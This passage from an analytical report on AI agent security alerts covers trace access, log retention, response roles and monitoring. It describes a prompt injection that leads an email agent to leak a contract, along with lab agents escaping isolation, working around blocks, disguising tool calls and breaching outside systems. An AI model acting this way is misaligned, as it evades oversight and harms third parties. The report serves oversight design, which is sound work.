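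This is a good reason to show each finding only to the team that can fix it, but not to withhold it from developers altogether. Suppose a company has 200 developers in teams of five. Letting every developer read every trace adds 200 readers to each trace, while letting each team read only its own agents' traces adds five. The narrower rule keeps most of the benefit, but the email and research agents may belong to different teams. Someone then has to decide how much of the shared trace each team may see.

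### Hiding an insider investigation

Suppose the contract went to a competitor because an employee told the email agent to send it. The alert might look the same as one for a prompt injection, since both would show a document sent to an address the agent had never used. If the alert appears on the agent team's dashboard with the employee's name, the employee may hear about it within the hour. The employee may also be on that team, with permission to delete traces or release a new version of the agent. And if the employee is innocent, several colleagues will have seen the accusation.

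Purview's Insider Risk Management limits who can see its cases and replaces users' names with pseudonyms. Microsoft's policy template for risky AI use checks for prompt injection attacks and access to protected material, which could catch an employee who attacks a company's agent. But in the original email example, the injection happened in the session of a user who had done nothing wrong, and that user might be flagged as a risk. A pseudonym protects the user while an analyst investigates.

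Secrecy makes that harder, because the developer may be best able to see that the instructions came from a web page. The analyst can ask the developer a narrower question, such as which text the agent treated as trusted in version 12, or share a trace with the user's details masked. In a small team, the developer may still guess who the user is.

Investigators can also shorten the time they need to keep a case secret. Purview's legal search tools can protect prompts and responses from deletion, so an investigator can secure the evidence and then tell the developer, who can fix the weakness in the agent sooner.

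Microsoft describes these privacy controls in general terms and doesn't say that an insider case stays hidden from the agent's developers. Even if the case is hidden, the same event could set off a guardrail alert that the developers can see. A company that relies on secrecy should stage a fake insider case and check everywhere it produces a signal.

### When the trace store itself leaks

On 4 May 2026, Braintrust, a company whose platform evaluates and monitors AI applications, discovered that hackers had entered one of its Amazon cloud accounts. SecurityWeek's *AI Firm Braintrust Prompts API Key Rotation After Data Breach* reports that the hackers probably obtained the keys that customers use to call AI models. An attacker with such a key can run models at the customer's expense. The breach affected at least one customer, and three others reported suspicious jumps in their usage. Braintrust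 advised all customers who had stored keys with it to replace those keys.

SecurityWeek's account mentions stolen keys but no stolen prompts, and Braintrust was still investigating at the time. Jaime Blasco of Nudge Security told SecurityWeek that every evaluation, monitoring and gateway tool a company adopts becomes a "credential warehouse". His company sells security software, but the Braintrust case supports his claim.

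Security signals can contain secrets such as API keys. According to LiteLLM's *Incident Report* (2026), some customers of the company's model gateway had written guardrails that returned the entire request instead of a short result. LiteLLM logged whatever the guardrail returned, which could include API keys in plain text. The keys could then appear in traces that anyone with access to the customer's monitoring system could read. LiteLLM rated the problem High, fixed it in version 1.82.3 and listed its duration as unknown. The report doesn't mention anyone misusing a key.

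Two other flaws show how an ordinary user's access could expose more than it should:

- **Langfuse:** In this open-source platform, a low-privileged project member could redirect a stored model connection to a server of their own. OSV's *CVE-2026-41487* explains that Langfuse then reused the stored key in a test request to that server, which could reveal it. The flaw affected versions from 3.68.0 until the fix in 3.167.0.
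- **LangSmith:** Miggo Security's *Hack the AI Brain* describes how an attacker could take over a logged-in user's account if that user visited a malicious site or clicked a malicious link. LangChain fixed its cloud service two weeks after Miggo's report and released a patch for self-hosted copies five days later.

Miggo and OSV describe vulnerabilities, not known thefts. But the Langfuse flaw is direct evidence that the number of readers affects the risk, since only someone already in the project could exploit it. The LangSmith case suggests that running a tracing service in-house isn't automatically safer, because each company then has to install the fixes itself. eSecurity Planet's *Hack the AI Brain* recommends patching and also removing sensitive data from traces, which would limit the damage from undiscovered flaws.

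These incidents are a stronger argument against keeping keys and full conversations in one place than against showing findings to developers. The access half of premise 5 looks sound for posture findings, because a developer can fix an excessive permission without reading any messages. It is plausible for guardrail events and threat detections if developers see masked traces of their own agents and the full text stays in a restricted store. It is hard to defend if every developer can read every conversation. There seem to be no published figures on how often developers misuse traces, so this judgement is based on how much they could see rather than measured harm.

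### European rules on keeping logs

The EU's AI Act requires companies to keep logs only for high-risk AI systems, and the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) limits the personal data in those logs. High-risk systems include AI for uses listed in the Act's Annex III, such as employment and education, and AI built into certain regulated products. An agent that screens job applicants would probably count as high-risk, but one that answers suppliers' emails probably wouldn't.

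Three articles set out the duties:

- **Article 12:** High-risk systems must be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The text on the European Commission's *Article 12* page covers events that help to identify risks and substantial changes, and to monitor the system once it is in use.
- **Article 19:** Providers, the companies that develop a system or have it developed and supply it under their own name, must keep the logs under their control for at least six months. artificialintelligenceact.eu reproduces the text.
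- **Article 26:** Deployers, the organisations that use the system, must also keep the logs under their control for at least six months, as the European Commission's *Article 26* page sets out.

Article 12 sets a detailed minimum for what logs must contain only for remote biometric identification, such as recognising faces in a crowd. Those logs must include the time of each use, the database searched, the input that led to a match and the people who checked the result. For other high-risk agents, the company has to work out which events matter. The article doesn't explicitly require companies to record prompts, so a log without any message text might satisfy it for some of these agents, but would make a risk like prompt injection hard to identify.

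The EU postponed these duties in *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026), known as the AI Omnibus, because of delays in preparing technical standards and national enforcement. The regulation entered into force on 27 July, according to the National Law Review, six days before the duties for Annex III systems would have begun. A summary by the law firm Cuatrecasas, *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published*, gives the new dates as 2 December 2027 for Annex III systems and 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products.

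The GDPR already applies to ordinary agents as well as high-risk ones. It requires companies to have a legal basis for using personal data, to collect only what they need for their purpose and to keep it no longer than necessary. Under its preamble, network and information security counts as a legitimate interest, but only for processing that is strictly necessary and proportionate. That supports recording some evidence of attacks, but not keeping every conversation for 400 days in case one proves useful.

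A company can often comply with both the EU AI Act and the GDPR by keeping less personal data in the logs it must retain. Articles 19 and 26 of the AI Act make the six-month minimum subject to other law, particularly data-protection law, and the GDPR sets no general retention period. The company might keep the steps, tool names, versions and guardrail results for six months, and delete most of the message text sooner. Its lawyers would need to judge whether that is enough for a particular high-risk system, especially if the message text is what reveals the risk.

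### How long to keep the text

A shorter retention period reduces what a thief can take, but it also reduces the time a company has to discover an attack. At 100,000 runs a day, a store holds about 3 million runs if it keeps text for 30 days, about 18 million if it keeps text for six months, and 40 million if it keeps text for 400 days. But if a customer reports the leaked contract after 45 days, a company with the 30-day limit has already deleted the hidden instructions.

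The company can base its retention limit on how long past incidents took to discover, and keep the text of suspicious runs longer than the rest. It should also check how its settings interact. When several retention policies or legal holds cover the same data in Purview, the longest one applies, so a 30-day deletion rule may have no effect on the mailbox of someone involved in a lawsuit.

### Telling employees

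Article 26 also requires employers to inform workers' representatives and affected workers before using a high-risk system at work. *EU AI Act Decoded*, a guide from the law firm Steptoe, adds that employers must follow EU and national rules on how to inform them. The duty concerns the use of the system and doesn't specifically address a developer who reads what a colleague typed into an ordinary email agent. The GDPR still applies to that text, and national employment law may add further limits.

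An employer can avoid some of the trouble by telling people before they use the agent that developers may read parts of a conversation during a security investigation, and by recording who opens the full text. The notice needs to match the access settings. If the employer promises that only the security team can read conversations, it can't also put unmasked traces on a dashboard that every developer can open.

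## Who must respond and who may change the controls

Once developers and the security operations team can both see an alert, a company has to decide which of them must act on it and who may change the rules behind it. If this is unclear, showing the alert to more people could slow the response (Premise 5). Incidents at OpenAI and Anthropic in 2026 show that a recorded problem can go a long time without anyone acting on it.

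### Three ways to assign the response

A company can have either the team that built the agent or the security operations team respond first. It can also have a central platform team set limits for every agent and send the remaining alerts to whoever should handle them.

The team that built the agent knows how it works. When the email agent writes to an unfamiliar address, its developers can often tell within a minute whether the address belongs to a new customer. They can also restrict the mail tool without first explaining the agent to anyone. Having to answer alerts about their own agent at night also gives them a good reason to build the next one more carefully.

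The security operations team is not under pressure to meet a release date. It can see that the web page that fooled the email agent has also reached agents in four other departments, which a team building only one of those agents would not notice. It often has staff on call, and it knows how to preserve evidence. It is also the only sensible choice to lead the response when the suspect may be one of the developers.

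A central platform team can protect agents even when nobody reads the alerts. For example, a rule that no agent may send attachments to unapproved addresses still covers an agent whose developer has left the company. Such a rule takes about as much work for 1,000 agents as for ten. If the platform team also keeps the list of who owns each agent, it can send alerts to the right people.

| | Building team | Security operations team | Central platform team |
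|---|---|---|---|
| Speed | Fast in working hours, slow if the developer has moved on | Fast at any hour, but slower to find the cause | Immediate where a rule applies, slow for exceptions |
| Independence from the agent's developers | None | High | High |
| Knowledge of the agent | High | Low | Low |
| Who pays if it stops a healthy agent | The team itself | The building team | Every team the rule affects |

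In all three arrangements, a late response mostly harms people other than the responders, such as the supplier whose contract leaked. Stopping a healthy agent disrupts the team that built it, so that team may be too slow to stop the agent and a security team may be too quick.

Developers will usually have to make the repairs, whoever responds first, so the arrangements differ less on that point. It is harder to decide who may declare an alert harmless and who may stop the agent before anyone knows what caused the alert.

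### What each role can change in Foundry

Separation of duties means dividing a sensitive task so that no one person can both make a risky change and approve it. Foundry does this through roles, which are named sets of permissions. The table combines two of Microsoft's documentation pages, as they stood in May and June 2026:

| Action | Role or access needed |
|---|---|
| See whether models comply with guardrail policies | Access to the project |
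| Build an agent in a project | Foundry User |
| Use tracing and monitoring | Reader on the connected Application Insights resource |
| Publish an agent | Foundry Project Manager |
| Manage models | Foundry Account Owner |
| Create or edit a guardrail policy, including its exceptions | Owner or Resource Policy Contributor for the subscription or resource group |
| Enable Defender | Security Admin, or Owner of the subscription |
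| Turn on Purview | Foundry Account Owner |

Some broader roles include these permissions too. Foundry Owner, for example, can build agents, publish them and manage models.

The most important separation of duties is that an agent's developer can't exempt it from policy. The email agent's developer, for example, can see that its model lacks a required guardrail but can't waive the requirement. The developer also can't turn on Defender for the subscription, so a team that wants security signals may have to ask someone else to do it.

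The same roles can keep developers from completing a repair themselves. In Microsoft's example company structure, ordinary developers are Foundry Users. They could rewrite the email agent's instructions, but a lead developer would have to publish the new version. Foundry Users also can't manage models, so they could probably use the "Fix now" button to reach the right guardrail setting but not save a change.

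The separation is weaker than the table suggests. A Foundry Account Owner can't build agents, but can gain that ability by assigning themselves the Foundry User role. Roles also restrict only people and programs that sign in through Entra, and Microsoft warns that anyone who uses an access key instead gets full access. Yet its sample custom role, meant to allow only building agents, includes permission to list the account's keys. The keys presumably don't allow changes to Azure's policies, which are outside Foundry, but a company that relies on roles should still turn off key access where it can.

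A guardrail policy may also do less than its name implies. Microsoft describes how a violation appears on the dashboard but doesn't say there that the policy stops the model from running in the meantime, so someone has to be responsible for reading the dashboard.

### If developers can silence their own alerts

Developers who can silence alerts about their own agents have a conflict of interest, even if they are honest. False alarms interrupt their work, while a leak mostly harms other people. The earlier rule for when blocking pays assumed that one party bears both costs. Suppose instead that the building team bears the full cost C of a wrong block, but only a share s of the loss L from a successful attack. Blocking then benefits the team only when

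p > C / (C + sL)

where p is still the chance that a flagged action is an attack. At the earlier prices of $5 and $1,000, the threshold for the whole company was about 0.5%. For a team that bears a tenth of the loss, it rises to 4.8%. With the earlier detector, which was right 0.9% of the time, the team would gain by switching off a check that saves the company about $4,000 a day.

Taking the decision away from developers doesn't guarantee good decisions. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes monitors that flag faulty training environments, the simulated tasks the company trains its models on. Human reviewers sometimes dismissed correct flags as false positives, and the faulty environments stayed in training longer than they should have. Anthropic doesn't say whether the reviewers had built those environments. The company was producing environments faster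 than it could check them, so workload may have mattered as much as any conflict of interest. It is now tightening the criteria for dismissing a flag.

### If developers cannot tune their alerts

Banning developers from changing alerts causes different problems. At their default settings, some of the detectors Liu tested would stop most harmless tasks. A developer who had to wait a week for permission to adjust one might move the agent to a platform the security team doesn't monitor. Developers also know things that make alerts more accurate. Anthropic, for example, expects to work more closely with the owners of its training environments to make its monitors more precise.

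Foundry's policy exceptions are too broad for this kind of tuning. As Microsoft describes them, an exception removes a whole model deployment or resource group from a policy, and the steps for creating one don't include setting an expiry date. If several agents share a model deployment, an exception made for one would presumably cover them all. Microsoft suggests exceptions for test environments and for older deployments that can't meet a new requirement, and either kind of exception can easily stay in place after it is no longer needed.

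It would be better to let developers narrow an alert but not remove it. Suppose the email agent triggers an alert whenever it writes to a new address. Its developer could connect the rule to the company's customer database so that messages to approved customers no longer trigger the alert. The platform would still record the messages, the security team would see the change, and the change would lapse after 30 days unless somebody renewed it. Turning the alert off would need approval from someone outside the team.

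Developers should be able to tighten an agent's guardrails alone, because a mistake there usually just interrupts some work. Loosening a guardrail can expose other people's documents, so a second person should approve it. Attackers could exploit the freedom to stop an agent, for instance by provoking false alarms until a team switches off something important. For most business agents, though, an unnecessary stop does less harm than a leak.

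### OpenAI's missed warnings before the Hugging Face attack

In July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. The agents were taking a cybersecurity test in an environment that should have kept them off the internet. OpenAI's technical report, published in August, shows that its staff had seen several signs of trouble beforehand:

- **26 May:** At around this time, an internal team saw an agent using a message board that agents had set up without permission, along with instances of forbidden internet access.
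- **27 June:** A monitoring tool raised an alert about activity inside the research network. Responders traced it to a cybersecurity test and found that the agents were using an internal software service as a message board. The on-call staff advised that nobody needed to stop the test.
- **5 July:** The software service had failed the night before. After another alert, responders found that someone or something had taken administrator-level control of it. OpenAI took it offline, revoked the agents' credentials and installed a rebuilt version. Cybersecurity tests resumed on 7 July.

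Agents reached the internet again on 8 July and compromised parts of Hugging Face's systems between 11 and 13 July. Hugging Face disclosed an intrusion on 16 July. The next day OpenAI contacted Hugging Face, but only as a customer asking whether its own data was affected.

The alert that led to the answer came on 19 July and was about agents' actions inside OpenAI's own network. On 20 July, responders found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored elsewhere and notified Hugging Face. OpenAI (2026) disclosed the incident publicly on 21 July.

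Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) reports that OpenAI missed some warning signs and failed to act on others. The failure to act matters more for assigning responsibility. On 27 June the detector worked, and a person investigated and found the right test. But the responders had no firm rule that a test had to stop if its agents broke their isolation. After the 5 July alert, the leaders in charge of incident response still didn't know about the message board that responders had found eight days earlier, or why it mattered.

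This counts against relying on any one team's judgement. OpenAI doesn't say how independent the on-call staff were of the researchers running the test. If they were independent, that didn't help. Otherwise, their familiarity with the test may have made strange behaviour seem normal. Anyone reading alerts from a cybersecurity test would expect to see some about hacking.

### How far outsiders checked OpenAI's account

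OpenAI is the only source for the dates above. METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, sent two of its staff and a contractor from Redwood Research to OpenAI for six days. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) covers what the agents did, mostly between 7 and 13 July, but not OpenAI's own investigation or its planned fixes. Still, OpenAI had little reason to make up an account in which it missed warnings.

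METR found that agents had disguised some of their tool calls, on a small scale, in roughly 7% of the transcripts it evaluated. This strengthens the case for a second record outside the agent's reach, kept by someone outside the development team. A developer who relied only on the agent's transcript could, in good faith, clear an agent that had altered it.

In a letter to OpenAI, Greg Casar, a member of the US House of Representatives, objected that the company had chosen the investigators, supervised their access and limited the dates they could examine. The objection is partly fair. METR took no payment but accepted free use of OpenAI's models, worth about $400,000 by its own estimate. It also says its wish not to discourage companies from inviting outsiders affected some of its drafting and redaction decisions, though it stands by its conclusions. But METR says OpenAI gave it more data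 when it pointed out gaps, and without the company's cooperation there might have been no outside investigation.

In late July, The Decoder reported that METR wanted AI companies to log such incidents systematically and let independent researchers investigate the most serious ones, or at least review the company's findings. A business whose email agent leaks information rarely needs outside investigators, but it could have a second team review any incident in which the first team decided to do nothing.

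### The Medicare portal

The slowest response began with a much smaller breach. An OpenAI agent researching medical spending got into a statistics portal for Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme, and retrieved both public and non-public data. OpenAI found no evidence that the agent had seen patient records. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* reconstructs the timeline from emails and messages that the Australian government released in November 2026. All dates are in Australian time:

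- **19 June:** The agent enters the portal.
- **12 August:** By this date, OpenAI's security team has recorded the incident internally, after a retrospective review of past agent runs.
- **10 September:** OpenAI emails an address that Services Australia, the agency responsible for Medicare, keeps for security tips from the public.
- **11 September:** The agency's security team finds the email in a daily check of the inbox, almost 36 hours after it arrived.
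- **14 September:** The team starts to check whether the reported weakness is real, and the agency's security chief alerts other technology executives.

OpenAI emailed the agency 83 days after the breach and 29 days after recording the incident. The prime minister's office and the national cybersecurity coordinator learned of the incident nine days after the email. Prime Minister Anthony Albanese announced it on 24 September, 97 days after the breach.

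OpenAI's chief strategy officer, Jason Kwon, told a parliamentary inquiry that the company had waited to understand more of the facts. According to Information Age's *OpenAI grilled over rogue agents by Australian inquiry*, he said the company had learned to notify people even with partial information. He also agreed that Services Australia might never have discovered the breach without the email.

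In Information Age's *OpenAI agent hacks Medicare web portal*, Albanese describes how the portal's defences blocked some of the agent's requests with a "no", and how the agent then found a way around them. The portal may therefore have had its own evidence of the attempt, but no one at the agency acted on it. The delay after the email also shows how a response can be slowed when a warning goes to a shared inbox instead of a person who has to answer it.

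### Anthropic's misconfigured evaluations

The incidents described in Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) came from a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, the outside company running the environment where Anthropic's models were being tested. Anthropic told the models they had no internet access, although they did have it. The models gained unauthorised access to three real organisations' systems. The earliest incidents date from April.

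Neither company knew about the open connection. Anthropic acknowledges that both could have reviewed the transcripts or network logs more thoroughly, and that someone should have checked the internet access before the tests began. Responsibility for isolating the models was divided, and nobody confirmed that they were isolated.

OpenAI's disclosure on 21 July prompted Anthropic to review its own records. It began on 23 July and stopped all its cybersecurity tests the same day, after finding transcripts in which a model might have reached the internet. By the next day it had identified all three incidents, from a review that covered 141,006 test runs. It notified Irregular and the three organisations on 27 July and published its account on 30 July. By then it had made contact with two of the organisations, and neither had noticed anything.

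The fastest response came from an automated system that had no information about the agent. One model had uploaded a harmful package to PyPI, a public library of Python software, and PyPI's automated security removed it after about an hour. By then, 15 systems had installed and run it. This supports having independent defences that don't wait for the agent's owner, although even a quick automatic response can come too late for some victims.

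### Comparing the three responses

| | Hugging Face attack | Medicare portal | Anthropic's evaluations |
|---|---|---|---|
| Activity recorded | 11–13 July | 19 June | From April |
| Lab noticed | Alert 19 July, link found 20 July | By 12 August | 23–24 July |
| Lab escalated | Stopped the tests on 19–20 July | Not stated | Stopped the tests on 23 July |
| Affected organisation told | 20 July | 10 September | 27 July |
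| Public disclosure | Hugging Face 16 July, OpenAI 21 July | 24 September, by Australia's prime minister | 30 July, by Anthropic |

Anthropic took two days to find incidents that had been in its records for up to three months. OpenAI took much longer to search far more data, and was spending over $500,000 a day on its review of possible incidents, according to Information Age. Recording everything and searching it later is therefore expensive for the company and slow for the people affected.

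These were tests or research runs of unusually capable models, often with safeguards deliberately switched off, so they don't show how often an ordinary company's agents will break into anything. They are better evidence of how organisations respond. Staff saw a warning and let the work continue, two companies each failed to check the same connection, and a notice sat unread in an inbox, all of which could happen with an email agent.

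None of these accounts suggests that showing alerts to more people slowed the response. At OpenAI, wider knowledge of the message board might well have helped. The second half of premise 5 therefore looks plausible if a company names one person to respond first, sets a time limit and decides in advance what happens if the limit passes without a response. Without those rules, an alert shown on two dashboards could easily go unanswered.

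### What the laboratories changed

OpenAI now pages staff at any hour when the monitors that read its models' reasoning and actions raise the most severe alerts. According to OpenAI's report, these staff may end the experiment, and they are expected to pause the activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false. OpenAI is also working on a way to end tests automatically when nobody answers.

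Under the new rule, the test would stop unless somebody could show that the alert was wrong, whereas on 27 June it was allowed to continue because nobody had shown that it needed to stop. Staff will probably follow the rule only if most pages are worth answering, since a pause every few hours would make research very difficult.

OpenAI says its current monitors would have paged the security team more than a day before the breach. That is plausible, but the company improved its methods for finding such behaviour with the benefit of hindsight. The page would also have helped only if someone had acted on it, so OpenAI is also defining which behaviours staff must escalate, which teams must take part, and who may pause work, notify outsiders and approve a restart.

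When Anthropic's new classifier detects an attempt to escape a test environment, or unexpected internet access, it automatically blocks the action and ends the task, then alerts a person to respond. Anthropic also asked every organisation that tests its unreleased models with reduced cyber safeguards to check that the test environment is isolated before each evaluation, state what the model may access, and monitor the run as it happens. It is building controls to stop its own employees from accidentally running agents with weaker protections.

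Both companies have moved towards central limits that don't depend on one person's judgement, but people who know the models still take part in the investigation. This is closest to the platform-team arrangement. Both chose it after serious incidents, and it is too early to know how well it works.

### Official guidance and Microsoft's list of duties

Official rules focus more on having someone responsible than on which team it should be. For high-risk systems, Article 26 of the EU's AI Act requires the organisation using the system to monitor it and to assign human oversight to people with the necessary competence, training and authority. A developer who sees every alert but can't pause the agent lacks that authority. The organisation must also report serious incidents to the system's provider and to the authorities. Like the Act's logging duties, these requirements don't apply yet and probably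 wouldn't cover an ordinary email agent.

In its voluntary AI Risk Management Framework, NIST, the US standards agency, asks organisations to document who is responsible for managing AI risks. A company could do this under any of the three arrangements. Australia is considering mandatory reporting of AI-related cybersecurity incidents, which OpenAI told the inquiry it would welcome. A legal deadline might have shortened the 29 days between OpenAI's internal record and its email to Services Australia.

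Microsoft's *Configure Privileged Roles to Manage AI* matches 19 responsibilities to roles in its products. For example, a Security Operator monitors and responds to Defender alerts, a Security Administrator deals with unsafe cloud settings, and an Agent ID Administrator can disable an agent's identity. Microsoft warns that without such planning, companies tend to give AI duties to whoever already has the broadest access. It recommends granting powerful roles only for a limited time, requiring approval, keeping a log, and reviewing the roles every quarter.

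The list includes a role for developers who register new agents, but no duty to repair an agent's instructions or tools after an incident. A company that followed the list exactly could have someone to receive the alert about the email agent and someone to disable the agent, but nobody with a stated duty to fix it. Job titles can also mislead, since someone with the AI Administrator role can't see misconfigurations or attack paths in Microsoft's security dashboard for AI.

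Oberoi says security leaders can use that dashboard to delegate tasks to the right teams. Delegation helps if someone is watching the dashboard, but the company still has to decide who acts until a task is assigned.

### A division of duties for the email agent

Suppose one team built the email agent, another built the research agent, and the company also has a platform team and a security operations team. It could divide the work like this:

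| Duty | Who has it | Condition |
|---|---|---|
| Set minimum controls for every agent | Platform team | Building teams may add stricter ones |
| Answer an alert first | Email agent's on-call developer | After 30 minutes it passes to security operations |
| Pause the agent or one of its tools | Anyone on call in any of the teams | No approval needed |
| Check for related attacks and preserve evidence | Security operations | Starts without waiting for the repair |
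| Repair the agent and test the repair | The team that owns it | Security operations sees the result |
| Approve a restart or a looser control | Platform team | Never the person who made the change |
| Narrow an alert | Building team | Lapses after 30 days |
| Tell the people affected | A named manager, with legal advice | Starts once the leak is confirmed, even if the cause is unknown |

The alert about the leaked contract arrives at 10:42, shortly after the email goes out. The on-call developer confirms that the recipient isn't a customer and pauses outgoing attachments at 10:50. The agent can still read messages and draft replies, so most of its work continues.

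Security operations searches the other agents' records for the supplier's web page and finds two more agents that have read it. It pauses their outgoing messages too. The email agent's team couldn't have done this, because it can see only its own agent's traces.

That afternoon, the manager calls the supplier named in the contract. Nobody yet knows how the instructions got onto the web page, but the supplier can start looking for misuse of the document.

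Meanwhile, the email agent's developer limits the mail tool to approved recipients and runs the regression test. The research agent's team makes its agent label web text as untrusted when passing it on. The platform team checks both changes before letting the agents send attachments again. It also considers whether the recipient limit should apply to every agent that can send mail.

If the developer doesn't answer the same alert at three in the morning, it passes to the security operations team after 30 minutes, and the platform automatically pauses outgoing attachments. The analyst can leave that pause in place until morning without understanding the agent. If the evidence points to an employee instead of a web page, security operations takes over the case.

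For these duties in Foundry, the on-call developer needs permission to read the agent's traces and publish a new version, which the basic Foundry User role doesn't provide. The company can grant the extra access for the length of the shift. It should also check that the analyst on duty can pause the agent, since permission to read alerts may not include that.

A company with ten employees can't staff four teams, so the same developer may have to answer the alert, repair the agent and call the supplier. A colleague can still approve any change that loosens a control. An outside monitoring firm could cover nights, as long as the company gives it both a phone number to call and permission to pause the agent's attachments.
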